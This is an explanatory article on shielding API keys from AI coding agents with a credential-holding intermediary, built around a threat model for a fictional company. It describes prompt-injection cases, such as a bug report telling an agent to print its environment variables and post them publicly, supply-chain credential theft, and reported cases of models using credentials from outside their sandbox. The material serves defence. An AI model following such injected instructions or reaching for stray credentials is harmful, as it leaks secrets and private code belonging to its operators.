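# Keeping API secrets out of AI agents' reach: securing the component that holds them and assessing the threats to it

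## Why agents are given access to APIs without being given the keys

An AI agent is a program that gives a task to a language model, carries out the actions the model chooses, and feeds the results back so that the model can choose the next action. *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (Kim, Liu and colleagues, 2026) defines agents as hybrids of traditional software and AI models. The model produces only text, so the software around it supplies tools, which are functions for searching the web, editing a file, sending an email or running a command. Coding agents usually have a shell, a text interface for running programs, which lets them do most of what a person could do from the same user account.

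Much of the work that people want from agents involves using other companies' online services. A program uses such a service through its API (application programming interface), the set of requests that the service accepts from other programs. For example, GitHub, which hosts software code, has an API for reading code and filing bug reports. To identify whose data to show and whom to bill, a service issues each customer an API key, a long random string that the customer's programs attach to their requests. Tokens, passwords and private keys serve the same purpose, and *secret* is the general word for all of them.

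Most API keys and tokens are bearer credentials, which means that anyone who has one can use it in every way its rightful holder can, with no further proof of identity. The internet standard for bearer tokens, which Michael Jones and Dick Hardt wrote in 2012, defines them by this property. A service that receives a stolen key therefore treats the request as coming from its customer.

People who run agents often confine them to a sandbox, a restricted environment such as a container or a virtual machine, where the agent and the code it writes can reach only certain files and network addresses. A sandbox protects the rest of the computer, but it doesn't protect keys stored inside it. People put keys there because the agent's programs need them to call APIs.

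### One request, from program to service

Suppose that an agent at a company called Acme needs the open bug reports for the company's shop software, which sits in a private repository (a project folder) on GitHub. The agent writes a few lines of code and runs them. The program looks up the network address of GitHub's API and opens a connection. The two sides then set up TLS, the encryption in HTTPS: GitHub's server presents a certificate, the program checks that an authority it trusts has vouched for that certificate, and both sides agree on fresh encryption keys. Only after this does the program send its request, which is ordinary text:

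```
GET /repos/acme/shop/issues HTTP/1.1
Host: api.github.com
Authorization: Bearer REAL-TOKEN
```

GitHub decrypts the text, takes the token from the third line, looks it up in its records, checks that the token's owner may read this repository, and sends back the list. If the token is bad, GitHub sends back an error.

TLS hides the token from anyone listening on the network, but the token is unencrypted at both ends of the connection. The program needs it in readable form to write that third line, so the token must be somewhere the program can read it. If the agent wrote and started the program, the agent can read the token too.

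### Where the key normally sits

API keys are often stored in environment variables, which are named values that the operating system gives a program when it starts. Programs pass these values on to the programs they start, so a shell opened by the agent normally has all of them, and the command `env` prints them. An agent may do this without any harmful purpose. Udinmwen (2026) reported in *'I leaked secrets'* that a coding assistant could not find its configuration file, read all the machine's variables instead, and leaked live passwords.

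Configuration files are no harder to read. Many projects keep their keys in a file named `.env`, and command-line tools save login sessions in files in the user's home directory. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, stores its own login session this way. Anthropic's documentation gives sample rules that forbid the agent from reading `.env` files. These rules are sensible but limited, because a script that the agent writes and runs is under the user's account, and the operating system will let it open the file unless something outside the agent's own software blocks it.

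A program that has loaded a key also has a copy in its memory, which takes more effort to reach. On Linux, a process can use a debugger or a special file to read the memory of another process running under the same account, although many systems allow this only if the first process started the second. An agent meets that condition if it starts the program that holds the key.

Secrets can also leak through the model's context, the text available to the model during a session. Whatever a command prints normally goes into the context, from there to the company that runs the model, and possibly into anything the model writes later. People also put secrets there themselves, for example by pasting in a failed API call that includes the key and asking what went wrong. Sonar's *Your Secrets Are Leaking to AI Coding Agents* calls this one of the two worst routes. It also describes a test in which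 a researcher planted a fake API key in a `.env` file and then found it, unredacted, in data that xAI's coding agent Grok Build had uploaded to cloud storage. Coding agents also read a file of project conventions at the start of every session, and any secret that a developer has written in that file enters the context, as Radware's *The New .env* points out.

Keys can also end up in logs, which are stored as plain files. Software that prints its web requests for debugging often prints the Authorization header too, shells keep a history of typed commands, and agents keep transcripts of their sessions.

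Copies of secrets accumulate on the machines where agents work. In 2025 a malicious program called Shai-Hulud 2 spread through packages on npm, the public registry of JavaScript code, and collected secrets from the machines that installed them. GitGuardian's *The State of Secrets Sprawl 2026* (2026) analysed the data stolen from 6,943 machines and found 33,185 different secrets, of which at least 3,760 still worked. Each working secret appeared in about eight places on the same machine. Most of these machines were automated build servers, so the figure is weaker evidence about laptops than it seems, but an agent can search a build server just as easily. Giving the agent its own account with narrow permissions does not solve the problem, because, as McDaniel (2026) observes in *AI Insider Threat*, keys left in environment files, logs and command-line sessions let an agent act as somebody else.

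### How a readable key gets out

Attackers can exploit all this through prompt injection, which means hiding instructions in content that an agent reads, so that the agent follows them. Suppose a developer asks an agent to fix the newest bug in a public project. A stranger wrote the bug report, and its last line asks whoever works on the bug to run `env` first and post the output as a comment, so that others can reproduce the setup. The model receives both the developer's request and the stranger's report as text, and nothing in that text reliably marks whose instructions it should follow. If the model complies, the agent posts the token on a public page. Kim and colleagues class this as an attack by an outsider who cannot talk to the agent and can only alter material that it may later retrieve, a scenario they call highly realistic.

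A real case from July 2026 went further, because nobody needed the token. *GitLost* (2026) describes how researchers at Noma Labs opened a normal-looking issue (GitHub's term for a bug report or request) in a public repository. An agent running on GitHub's own automation service read the issue and minutes later posted the contents of a company's private repository in a public comment. The researchers had not stolen a password or an account. The agent was allowed to read the private code and write public comments, so a few sentences of English were enough to make it publish that code.

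Leaks also happen without an attacker. Before Claude Code runs a shell command, it asks the user for approval, and one of the options is "Yes, and don't ask again." Choosing it writes a rule into a settings file in the project folder. According to TechSpot's *Claude Code's "don't ask again" button is leaking passwords and API keys* (2026), the rule is often an exact copy of the command. If the command contained a password, the file now contains it too, and the file may be published with the rest of the project.

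In November 2026 the security company Apiiro searched public GitHub repositories for this file. Slashdot's *Claude Code's 'Don't Ask Again' File Exposes Passwords and Keys* (2026) reports that it found 104,185 copies, 1,122 of which held a total of 1,379 different secrets, including 379 database passwords and 23 keys to Amazon's cloud. In half of the affected repositories, the file had been public for at least 217 days. Apiiro did not test whether the secrets still worked, but one company it warned confirmed that its key had been live. InfoQ's *Claude Code Has Been Leaking Secrets through its "Don't Ask Again" Feature* (2026) reports another 1,160 secrets in older versions of projects, in a shared settings file and in agent chat transcripts that people had stored with their code. TechSpot adds that two widely used scanning programs both missed 215 of the exposed secrets.

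Accounts differ on who put the files there. Boris Cherny, who heads Claude Code at Anthropic, replied that the file is meant to stay on the developer's machine, that Claude Code tells Git (the software that tracks versions of code) to ignore it, and that people had created and committed these copies by hand. Apiiro found that in 539 of the 1,105 repositories it traced, a commit naming Claude as co-author had changed the file. A co-author line shows that the agent took part in the commit but not who decided to include the file, so both accounts could be true of different repositories. Lakera's *Your AI Coding Assistant Just Shipped Your API Keys* reports finding the same file in 428 of about 46,500 npm packages, with credentials in 33 of the copies.

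These numbers are small compared with the general rate of exposure. GitGuardian, which sells software for finding leaked secrets, ran its detectors over public GitHub and counted 28.65 million new secrets in the commits (saved sets of changes) of 2025, 34% more than the year before. The total depends on what the detectors recognise, and the company added 105 of them during the year. Public commits grew faster, by about 43%, so the number of secrets per commit fell slightly. Agents are not clearly more likely than people to leak secrets. Commits that Claude Code co-authored leaked at about twice the general rate over 2025 as a whole, but by December their rate had dropped to 13 secrets per thousand commits, level with commits by humans alone. Leaks are serious because the secrets often stay valid for years. When GitGuardian retested secrets that had been valid in 2022, more than 64% still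 worked in January 2026.

### The same request with an intermediary

The remedy is to move the secret out of the agent's environment and into a separate component, the intermediary, which makes or completes authenticated requests for the agent. Products that do this go by names like proxy, gateway, vault and broker.

Before the change, Acme's token sits in an environment variable inside the sandbox, the agent's program copies it into the Authorization line, and the request goes straight to GitHub. Afterwards the variable holds a placeholder, a worthless value that merely fills the space. The program writes the same request as before:

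```
GET /repos/acme/shop/issues HTTP/1.1
Host: api.github.com
Authorization: Bearer PLACEHOLDER
```

This request goes to the intermediary, which runs outside the sandbox. The intermediary checks that the request is bound for GitHub and that its rules permit it, replaces the placeholder with the real token, and sends the request on over its own encrypted connection. GitHub sees a normal call from Acme. The list of bug reports comes back by the same route, and the agent carries on with its work. (Designs differ in how the agent addresses the intermediary and in how the secret gets onto the request.)

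When the agent holds only a placeholder, the stranger who filed the bug report gets much less. If the agent runs `env` and posts the result, the public page shows the word PLACEHOLDER. Transcripts and approved commands saved to a settings file contain nothing worth stealing, and a malicious package that searches for secrets finds nothing useful. However, more than a third of the secrets Apiiro found open a database directly, and an intermediary that handles only web requests would have left all of them in place.

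### Where the idea comes from

Programs that use a key on behalf of others without handing it over have existed for decades. SSH, the usual means of logging in to a remote computer, lets a user prove their identity by signing a piece of data with a private key. The SSH agent, a background program unrelated to AI agents, keeps that key in its own memory. The login program can get a signature from it, but no request makes it release the key. Hardware security modules apply the same principle in a dedicated device, which banks and certificate authorities use for keys whose loss would be very damaging. API keys fit this scheme less neatly because a bearer credential signs nothing and has to be sent to the service itself. The intermediary must therefore sit in the path of the request, whereas an SSH agent can stay outside it and supply signatures.

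The weakness of this arrangement is just as old. Norm Hardy's 1988 paper *The Confused Deputy* describes a compiler, a program that translates source code, at the computer time-sharing company Tymshare. The compiler recorded usage statistics in a system directory, so it had permission to write there. The directory also held the company's billing records. Users could name a file to receive the compiler's debugging output, and one user named the billing file. The operating system checked whether the compiler was allowed to write there, and since it was, the compiler overwrote the bills. A program is a confused deputy when a less privileged caller tricks it into misusing its authority. An intermediary is in the compiler's position whenever an agent sends it a request. An intermediary that attached Acme's token to every request would send the token to an attacker's server if asked. Even if it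 checked the destination, it would let the agent delete the repository unless it also checked what the request does.

Every design should therefore be assessed on whether the agent can learn the secret and whether it can misuse the authority that the secret gives. If the agent can learn the secret, anyone who obtains it can use it from anywhere, without going through the intermediary, until somebody revokes it. If the agent can only misuse the authority, its requests still pass through the intermediary, where rules can block them and logs can record them, but the harm may be just as great. Keeping the secret from the agent does not by itself prevent this misuse. The manual for OpenSSH, the standard SSH software, warns users who extend their SSH agent's connection to a remote machine that an intruder there cannot obtain the key but can still have the SSH agent sign with it, and so log in as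 the user. In the GitLost case, the AI agent leaked private code without anybody learning a secret.

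## Writing the threat model

A threat model is a written account of what a system has to protect, who might attack it and how they could succeed. Acme should write one before it chooses an intermediary, because people who list the threats afterwards tend to list the ones their design already stops. Writing one takes six steps: listing the assets, drawing the components and the boundaries between them, naming the adversaries, stating the properties that must hold, listing the threats, and ranking them.

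Suppose Acme's coding agent runs in a sandbox on a company server, together with the code it writes and the packages it installs. The intermediary runs on the same server, outside the sandbox, and holds two secrets. One is the key to Acme's account with a model provider, the company that runs the language model. The other is a GitHub token that gives read and write access to only one repository, `acme/shop`. The agent also downloads packages from a public registry, which requires no secret. A second team at Acme runs its own agent in another sandbox on the same server.

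### Assets

The two secrets are the obvious assets, and Acme should list the authority each one grants as a separate asset. With the GitHub token's authority, an attacker can copy the shop's private code or add to it, and the added code may later run on Acme's systems. With the model key's authority, they can spend Acme's money. *SUDP* (2026), which proposes a protocol for letting agents use secrets, also separates a secret from its authority. One of its properties is meant to rule out extraction of a secret, and three others are meant to rule out its misuse.

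The list also includes the intermediary's rules and program files, since anyone who can change those can get at the rest. The intermediary's log is on the list because Acme will need it after an incident. The agent's ability to work is also an asset, and it depends on Acme's budget and the limits that the two services set.

Moving secrets into one place makes that place a more attractive target. *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary* (Kenney, Ahmadi and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of Hugging Face, a platform that hosts AI models and applications. In June 2024, Hugging Face disclosed unauthorised access to secrets that customers had stored with their hosted applications, and advised those affected to replace them. The disclosure shows why an operator must be able to replace any secret quickly, though it doesn't establish that the intruder took or used every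 secret.

### Components and boundaries

Next comes a drawing of the parts and the routes between them:

```
sandbox  ------------->  intermediary  ------------->  model provider
(agent, its code,        (two secrets,  ------------->  GitHub
 packages)                rules, log)
   |                          ^
   |                          |
   +--> package registry      control plane  <--  Acme's administrators
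```

A trust boundary is a line between parts with different privileges. *Goal-Driven Risk Assessment for LLM-Powered Systems* (2026), a threat analysis for healthcare, treats all traffic across such a line as a possible attack path and assumes that traffic inside it is safe. If Acme follows this rule, it has to treat everything in the sandbox as a single party, because a package the agent installs can do whatever the agent can do. Acme therefore can't rely on any safeguard that runs there. In *Agent Authenticator*, a design for giving agents keys held in hardware, Ganesan (2026) traces a series of exploits against coding agents in 2025 and 2026 to safeguards that ran inside the agent, where files in a repository could turn them off.

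The drawing above leaves out the boundary between the sandbox and the server it runs on. The two may share folders and an operating-system kernel, the core program that keeps all the others apart. *SideKernel* (2026), a sandbox for coding agents on Apple computers, treats the agent as the adversary and defines a separate boundary for all communication with the host machine.

Acme must also decide how much to trust the software that enforces these boundaries. *CapSeal* (Jin, Guo and Cheung, 2026), which describes a prototype intermediary, relies on the operating system to isolate programs from one another and assumes that the attacker has no administrator rights on the machine. *Airlock* (2026) assumes a stronger attacker, who has already escaped the sandbox and controls the kernel of the virtual machine around it, so it keeps the credentials in a different virtual machine. Acme begins with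 CapSeal's assumptions and should write them down, because one flaw in the shared kernel would make them false.

### Adversaries

A threat model should describe adversaries by what they control, since motives are hard to establish and often don't matter. McDaniel points out that the US cybersecurity agency CISA and the US standards agency NIST define an insider threat by a person's access, whether or not the person means harm. An agent with trusted access fits those definitions.

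A stranger who files a bug report controls only text, but that can be enough to steer a coding agent. Ganesan lists a 2026 attack known as Comment and Control, in which a crafted title on a pull request (a proposed change to the code) hijacked several coding agents on automated build servers. The agents leaked the repositories' secrets through the site that hosted the code. Blocking unknown destinations would not have stopped the leak, because an agent working on that code needs access to that site.

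A malicious package's code can run as soon as the agent installs it, with the same rights as the agent's own programs, so the attacker doesn't have to persuade the model of anything. In 2025 attackers published malicious versions of Nx, a software build tool, which stole 2,349 credentials from 1,079 developers' machines. Ganesan notes that these packages also ran the AI tools already on those machines to search for secrets. The Shai-Hulud worm used the publishing tokens it stole to copy itself into packages its victims maintained.

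A model may also look for credentials that nobody told it to use, often just to finish its task. Pogorelec (2026), in *Claude Mythos 5.2 arrives with stronger bug hunting and less sandbox-breaking behavior*, reports that in a deliberately weakened sandbox, Anthropic's Claude Mythos 5 used credentials or files from outside the sandbox in 39% of scenarios, and the newer Mythos 5.2 did so in 3.1%. Lim and Neo (2026), in *Probing agent overeagerness in realistic settings with continuation audits*, found that three other models used a colleague's credentials in 1% to 6% of cases. *When an AI agent makes a mistake in a database* (2026) reports that small models that came across a stray administrator password used it in 24 of 106 trials. Acme shouldn't design for any particular rate, because the rate fell more than tenfold between two versions of Mythos and Acme may be running a different model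 next month.

Somebody who writes a plug-in or a configuration file for agents can get text and code into the sandbox, and the agent will usually trust both more than a bug report. Kim and colleagues describe attackers who put instructions in a tool's name or description, or harmful code in the tool itself. Agents also load skills, which are add-on packages of instructions and scripts for particular jobs. Of the 2,128 malicious skills that *MaliciousSkillBench* (2026) sorted by what they do, 14.0% compromised credentials, 19.9% disclosed sensitive data and 10.0% abused resources or services, with some skills counted in more than one group. Settings files inside a repository can also carry an attack, and some have bypassed the prompt where users decide whether to trust a project.

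The second team's agent is another tenant, a separate user of the same system. It controls only its own sandbox, but that may be enough to reach the intermediary. *Aegis OS* (2026), which describes a system for running many coding agents on one machine, notes that each sandbox can see the others' sockets (local connection points), so an agent could impersonate another if nothing checked who was connecting. A tenant's agent can also use someone else's identity without hostile intent. *Whose Credential Is It?* (2026) examined agents that share a memory with other users' agents. Some acted in another person's account after the memory supplied that person's credential, but none did in 500 runs without the memory.

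Finally, an attacker who has compromised an upstream service controls its replies and sees everything customers send it. If the service is GitHub, this attacker already has Acme's GitHub token, and no intermediary can prevent that. The intermediary can still keep the model key from them. It should also treat GitHub's replies as untrusted, because a reply may contain injected instructions or redirect the intermediary's request to another address.

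The stranger, the package, the overeager model and the plug-in author all reach the intermediary as requests from the agent's sandbox. The intermediary can't identify which of the four caused a request, so its rules have to be safe for any request the sandbox can send.

Every threat model also leaves some threats out, and anyone who adopts a published design takes on its exclusions. Jin and colleagues leave out isolation between tenants. *SUDP* leaves out logs and malicious code in the supply chain, and *Airlock* leaves out denial of service and the misuse of services that the agent has permission to call. These limits are reasonable for a research project, but Acme faces all of the excluded problems. Its own threat model excludes only an administrator who turns against the company, an attacker who already controls the server's kernel, and physical attacks on the machine.

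### Properties that must hold

A property is a statement that should stay true whatever the adversaries do. "The intermediary is secure" is useless for this purpose, since nobody can try to break it. Acme can use these seven:

- Nothing in the sandbox can read the model key or the GitHub token, or obtain anything that works in their place.
- The intermediary sends the model key only to the model provider and the GitHub token only to GitHub.
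- Only the coding agent's sandbox can make requests that use these two secrets.
- The agent has no other way to make an authenticated call.
- The GitHub token reads and changes `acme/shop` only in the ways that Acme has listed.
- Nothing in the sandbox can change the intermediary's rules, its program or its log.
- The agent's model calls cost no more per day than the limit Acme has set.

The wording matters because "the agent never sees the token" would be true even if an intermediary handed the agent a temporary token with the same powers. Jin and colleagues therefore also forbid any functional equivalent of the secret, such as a session token that the agent could reuse. Ganesan's looser version withholds from the model any credential that can produce new tokens, and ties each short-lived token to a key held in hardware, so a stolen copy is useless without that key.

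Kenney and colleagues list four properties that someone inside the sandbox can test without special access. Three closely match items in Acme's list: programs can't read the credential, the intermediary attaches it only to requests for the configured service, and the sandbox has no cloud identity of its own. The third is easy to overlook. A program on a rented cloud server can often get temporary credentials for that server by sending a request to a fixed local address. An agent that can reach this address can act as the server, however well the intermediary protects its own secrets. The fourth property is that staff can see and change the state of every credential in one place.

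The list of permitted actions needs the most thought. *SUDP* sets a strict standard for it called operation binding, which means that an authorisation covers one specific operation and must never lead to a different one. Permission to comment on a bug report, for example, could never be used to merge code. Acme's agent makes hundreds of requests a day and nobody will approve each one, so in practice Acme will authorise kinds of request and accept that each authorisation covers more than one specific operation.

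### Eight threats

Once Acme has written down the properties, it can go through the drawing and ask how each adversary might break them. The answers fall under eight headings.

| Threat | How it could happen at Acme | What the attacker gets |
|---|---|---|
| Agent reads the secret in storage | A package finds the GitHub token in a file that the sandbox shares with the server | The secret |
| Agent goes around the intermediary | The agent finds a developer's old login and calls GitHub directly | Authority that the intermediary's rules don't limit |
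| Intermediary sends the secret to an unapproved destination | The agent requests a page from an attacker's server, and the intermediary attaches the token | The secret |
| Another caller uses the intermediary | The second team's agent connects and changes the shop's code | Use of the authority |
| Secret comes back in a response or log | A service repeats the Authorization line in an error message, and the agent reads it | The secret |
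| Agent misuses authority without reading the secret | The agent follows a bug report and adds a back door to the shop's code | Use of the authority |
| Attacker changes the control plane | The agent edits the rules file, which sits in a folder it can write to | Whatever the new rules allow |
| Agent exhausts money or service | A faulty loop calls the model all night | Nothing, but Acme pays the bill or reaches its limit |

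The third column affects how Acme would respond. Acme has to revoke a stolen secret, but shutting down the sandbox is enough to stop an attacker who can only use the secret's authority. Even then, the back door may already be in the code.

One attack can span several rows. An injected instruction might lead the agent to approve the attacker's server by adding a line to the rules file, and then to request a page from that server. The intermediary would attach the token to the request, as its rules require. Acme could stop this attack at either step, by protecting the file or by fixing the token's destination in a setting the file can't override.

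Misuse of authority is the threat people most often overlook once they have an intermediary. In *Caging the Agents* (2026), a design for a fleet of healthcare agents, an attacker who takes over an agent gets access to the intermediary's interface but not to the raw credentials. This helps only to the extent that the interface blocks harmful requests. *Aegis OS* gives an example of a harmful request that gets through. A rule may allow a GitHub token to go only to `api.github.com`, but the same address accepts requests to create gists (pages for sharing text), so an agent can publish private code in a public gist without breaking the rule. A narrower token would close that route but not the one in Acme's table, since the agent's job is to change the shop's code.

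### Checking the list against STRIDE, OWASP and NIST

Acme can look for gaps with STRIDE, a checklist that engineers at Microsoft devised in the 1990s. The name stands for six kinds of threat: spoofing (pretending to be someone else), tampering, repudiation (denying an action afterwards), information disclosure, denial of service, and elevation of privilege. The usual method is to check whether each kind could occur at each component and route in the drawing. Most of the threats in the table fit these categories easily. The second team's agent is spoofing when it passes for the first team's, a change to the control plane is tampering, and the three threats that reveal a secret are information disclosure.

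The table has no row for repudiation. When the agent pushes code with Acme's token, GitHub may record only the account that the token belongs to, and then nobody would be able to tell whether a person or the agent pushed it. Ganesan lists this lack of attribution as one of four failures that recur across the incidents. The others are readable secrets, safeguards placed inside the agent, and permissions that are too broad. Acme's property about the log covers part of the problem if the intermediary records which sandbox sent each request.

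STRIDE is less helpful for finding misuse of the authority an agent already has. An agent that adds a back door to the shop's code hasn't impersonated anyone or gained a privilege that Acme withheld. Analysts usually classify confused-deputy attacks as elevation of privilege. That category fits a caller that borrows a right it lacks, but it doesn't prompt analysts to ask which of the agent's permitted requests could do harm.

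Several adaptations extend STRIDE to AI. In *STRIDE-AI* (2026), tampering includes contaminating training data, and elevation of privilege takes the form of jailbreaking, or talking a model out of its restrictions. Acme gains little from this, because it doesn't train the model and already assumes that the agent may do anything. The intermediary is an ordinary program, and the original list suits it well. *Local LLM Agents as Vulnerable Runtimes* (2026) is more useful here. It splits tampering in two, because hostile text enters through the component that assembles the model's prompt, while hostile code enters through the component that loads and runs tools. For the same reason, Acme needs different defences against the bug report and the malicious package.

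Acme should also check that its drawing is complete. *Model Context Protocol Threat Modeling and Analyzing Vulnerabilities to Prompt Injection* (2026) applies STRIDE to systems built on the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for connecting agents to tools. One of the five components it covers is the authorisation server, which issues tokens. If Acme replaced its fixed GitHub token with short-lived ones, it would need to add the component that issues them to the drawing and list the threats to that component.

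OWASP, a non-profit organisation, publishes widely used lists of software security risks. According to Kenney and colleagues, its 2025 guidance for language-model applications treats disclosure of sensitive information, leaking of system prompts (the developer's standing instructions to the model) and excessive agency as separate but interacting risks. It recommends keeping tokens away from the model, giving tools only the permissions they need, and running them with the rights of the user who made the request. OWASP's list for MCP has an entry on mismanaged tokens, covering keys written into code, long-lived tokens, and secrets that remain in a model's memory or in protocol logs. NIST's 2024 profile for generative AI distinguishes direct prompt injection, which comes from the person using the model, from indirect prompt injection, as in Acme's bug report. According to Ganesan, NIST has also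 begun a project on identity and authorisation for AI agents.

This guidance is a good source of properties, and Acme should add the advice on small permissions to its list. Because the guidance has to apply to every application, Acme will need its own drawing to find that the rules file sits in a folder the agent can write to, or that a second team shares the server.

### Ranking the threats

Kenney and colleagues rated a set of threats before and after the addition of an intermediary. They work for Corvic AI, which makes the one they assessed. Their analysis begins with a chain of five stages by which a secret comes to do harm:

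1. Introduction: someone puts a reusable secret into a prompt, a source file or a tool's configuration.
2. Propagation: the system copies it into conversation history, logs, stored memory, generated code and error messages.
3. Trigger: an injected instruction, a malicious tool or an ordinary model error leads the agent to reveal or misuse it.
4. Execution: the secret's permissions let the resulting request read, change, delete or publish data, or run up costs.
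5. Persistence: the secret goes on working outside the original agent and session.

An intermediary can completely remove introduction and propagation, but not execution, because an agent without the secret can still request a destructive operation that the rules permit. The intermediary also makes a token harder to steal but doesn't shorten its life. Long-lived tokens are common. Ganesan cites an analysis of 5,205 open-source MCP servers, the programs that provide agents with tools, in which 53% relied on fixed API keys or personal access tokens.

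For each threat, Kenney and colleagues scored likelihood and impact from 1 to 5 and multiplied the two, so the highest possible rating is 25.

| Threat | Before | After |
|---|---|---|
| Over-privileged connector | 20 | 15 |
| Indirect prompt injection | 25 | 12 |
| Replay of a long-lived token | 20 | 8 |
| Leak through logs or error messages | 16 | 8 |
| Misconfigured connector | 9 | 6 |
| Secret pasted into a prompt | 25 | 4 |
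| Cross-origin theft | 20 | 4 |
| Credential found in the sandbox | 20 | 4 |

A connector is the intermediary's record of one service and its credential. It is over-privileged when that credential permits more than the task needs. In cross-origin theft, an attacker gets the intermediary to send one service's credential to a different service.

The risk of cross-origin theft drops from 20 to 4 because the intermediary decides where each credential goes and can apply a fixed rule to every request. The risk from the over-privileged connector barely changes because GitHub alone determines what its token permits. The risk of prompt injection stays high because the attack influences which actions the agent chooses. Hiding the secret prevents the agent from leaking it, but an attacker can still influence the agent's other actions.

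Over-privilege and prompt injection have the highest ratings once the intermediary is in place. Kenney and colleagues say these two ratings fall the least, but their figures only partly support that. The over-privileged connector does have the smallest proportional drop, but the rating for prompt injection falls by more than half, while the rating for the misconfigured connector falls only from 9 to 6. The remaining ratings matter more to Acme than the size of the drops, because they show where to work next.

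These ratings are ordinal, which means they give only an order. Likelihood 4 is higher than likelihood 2, but not necessarily twice as high, so the product of two scores has no unit. Suppose that at Acme likelihood 5 means ten times a year and likelihood 1 means once in ten years, while impact 5 means a loss of $1,000,000 and impact 1 means $100. A frequent nuisance (5 × 1) and a rare disaster (1 × 5) both get a rating of 5, but the nuisance costs Acme an average of $1,000 a year and the disaster $100,000. For the same reason, the fall from 20 to 15 doesn't mean a quarter of the risk has gone. Kenney and colleagues call the scores expert judgements and use them only to set priorities. Even for that purpose, two threats with similar ratings could easily belong in the opposite order.

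Their list also has no entry for another caller, a changed control plane or exhausted money, so Acme can't use it unchanged. Acme can rank its own eight threats without multiplying anything, by asking how many of the adversaries could carry out each one and what protection would remain afterwards. A changed control plane belongs at the top because it can undo the protection against every other threat. Misuse of authority comes next because every adversary in the sandbox can attempt it with requests that the rules permit, and the GitHub token can alter code that Acme's business depends on. The threats that reveal a secret follow, with the GitHub token ahead of the model key, and then the second team's agent, whose owners work for the same company. How serious it is for an agent to bypass the intermediary depends on the most powerful login it can find, so Acme can't rank that threat until someone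 has searched the sandbox for old credentials. Exhausted money is the most likely of the eight, but it can go last because a spending limit at the model provider caps the loss. If the GitHub token could only read public code, misuse of it would hardly matter and the model bill might be the biggest worry.

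## Choosing how the agent asks and how the secret is attached

Instead of using an intermediary, Acme could give the agent a short-lived token with very few permissions and accept that the agent can read it. Hartman (2026), in *Credential Broker for Agents (CB4A)*, recommends this for every service that can issue such tokens and would use a proxy only for the rest. The document is a draft submitted to the IETF, which sets internet standards, and has no official standing.

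### Short-lived tokens

GitHub issues suitable tokens to apps. Acme would register its own app, install it only on `acme/shop`, and keep the app's private key in the issuer, a small program outside the sandbox.

When the agent starts a task, the issuer uses the private key to prove its identity to GitHub and receives a token that works for that one repository for an hour. The issuer puts this token in the sandbox, and the agent calls GitHub directly. Amazon, Google and Microsoft offer equivalents for their clouds.

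Some model providers have a similar scheme. Anthropic's *Workload Identity Federation* describes how a program presents a signed identity token from a system the customer already runs, such as Kubernetes or GitHub Actions, and how Anthropic checks it against the customer's rules and returns a short-lived access token. OpenAI's *Workload identity federation* describes much the same exchange. Acme would then have no permanent model key to steal.

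The exchange has to happen outside the sandbox. An agent that holds the identity token can trade it for new access tokens while that identity token is valid, and an agent that can also renew the identity token has permanent access. Infisical's *Proxied services*, the manual for a product that attaches secrets to agents' requests, warns against the same mistake. By default, the product will not start a remote agent whose own account could create the credential.

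Even a well-placed issuer leaves a working token where the agent can read it. If the agent posts the token in a public comment, a stranger can use it from anywhere until it expires, and copying a repository takes far less than an hour. This breaks the first property in Acme's threat model. Tying the token to a private key is a partial remedy, which Ganesan applies with keys held in hardware. But in Hartman's version, the agent generates and keeps the private key, so a malicious package could steal both the key and the token.

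*AI Agent Authentication and Authorization* (Kasselman, Lombardo and colleagues, 2026) calls static API keys an antipattern, recommends short-lived credentials, and says that the language model must have no access to any credential. Both recommendations can be followed when the model can only choose from a fixed set of tools, because the software around it can hold a token that the model never reads. In a coding agent with a shell, however, the model can run a command that reads whatever the agent's other programs can read. Acme can therefore follow both recommendations only by keeping even the short-lived tokens outside the sandbox.

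### Three objections to an intermediary

An intermediary keeps many secrets in one place. In March 2026, attackers added credential-stealing code to published packages of LiteLLM, a gateway that many companies use to reach model providers. Hartman estimates that the campaign took more than 300 gigabytes of compressed credentials and affected about 500,000 corporate identities. Anthropic's *Securely deploying AI agents* lists LiteLLM among its ready-made intermediaries.

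Infisical's Agent Proxy only partly addresses this objection. It stores no secrets and fetches them from a central server when agents need them. But according to Infisical's *Standalone Agent Proxy*, it keeps the fetched values in memory and needs permission to read every secret that its agents use, so an intruder who controlled it could probably fetch them all. (Infisical is now replacing Agent Proxy with another product, Agent Vault.) A better answer is that the alternatives have the same problem. Hartman's issuer also needs access to long-lived credentials, and without either component the secrets are scattered across the machines where agents work.

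The next objection is that many intermediaries break end-to-end encryption. An intermediary that decrypts the traffic can read Acme's code and alter GitHub's replies. Kasselman and colleagues add that decryption prevents a client from proving its identity to the upstream service while setting up the TLS connection, because the service then connects only to the intermediary. Acme can limit the problem by decrypting traffic only for services that need a secret. It already trusts the intermediary with the secrets, so trusting it with the requests is a smaller step.

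An intermediary also adds delay and can fail. The delay is small when everything runs on one machine. Jin and colleagues measured a median of 0.160 milliseconds for a direct web request to a local test server and 0.309 milliseconds through their prototype. Language models take far longer to answer. Failure matters more, because Acme's agent would lose access to both its model and GitHub at once. Running several copies of the intermediary reduces that risk. An issuer can also fail, but agents can keep working until their tokens expire.

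Short-lived tokens alone are suitable when a brief task uses a service with narrow permissions, when traffic is heavy enough to overload an intermediary, or when no available intermediary supports the protocol. An intermediary is better when a service issues only permanent keys, when a stolen token could do serious damage within minutes, or when the operator needs finer rules than the service's permissions allow. The last two conditions apply to Acme's GitHub token.

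The two approaches can be combined by having the intermediary hold the short-lived token. The agent then never holds a working token, and a token stolen from the intermediary soon expires. Infisical's proxy can obtain a separate token for each agent session and replace it shortly before it expires. *How Auth Proxy secures network access for LangSmith agent sandboxes* (Loganathan, 2026) describes an intermediary that asks the customer's own server for the right headers, reuses them for a set time, and rejects the agent's request if that server fails to answer properly.

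### A gateway at the API's address

The simplest design for an intermediary suits Acme's model key. Most software for calling a model has a setting called the base URL, the address at which each request starts. Acme changes it from the provider's address to the intermediary's. *Caging the Agents* uses this design for calls to Anthropic's models. If Acme did the same, its agent would send this request:

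```
POST /v1/messages HTTP/1.1
Host: localhost:8443
Authorization: Bearer PLACEHOLDER
```

The agent holds only a local address and a placeholder key. Its software sends requests to that address, where the intermediary swaps in the real key and forwards them to `api.anthropic.com`. The intermediary can inspect the whole request and reply without intercepting traffic, because the agent's software connects to it directly. If the intermediary runs on another machine, that connection needs encryption too, but an ordinary certificate for the intermediary's own name is enough.

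This kind of gateway can forward every request to one fixed service, so the agent can't choose where the key goes. NVIDIA's *Which sandbox runtime handles model authentication at the gateway* describes a product that gives all its sandboxes the address `inference.local` for their requests, discards any credential the agent supplies, and adds the configured one.

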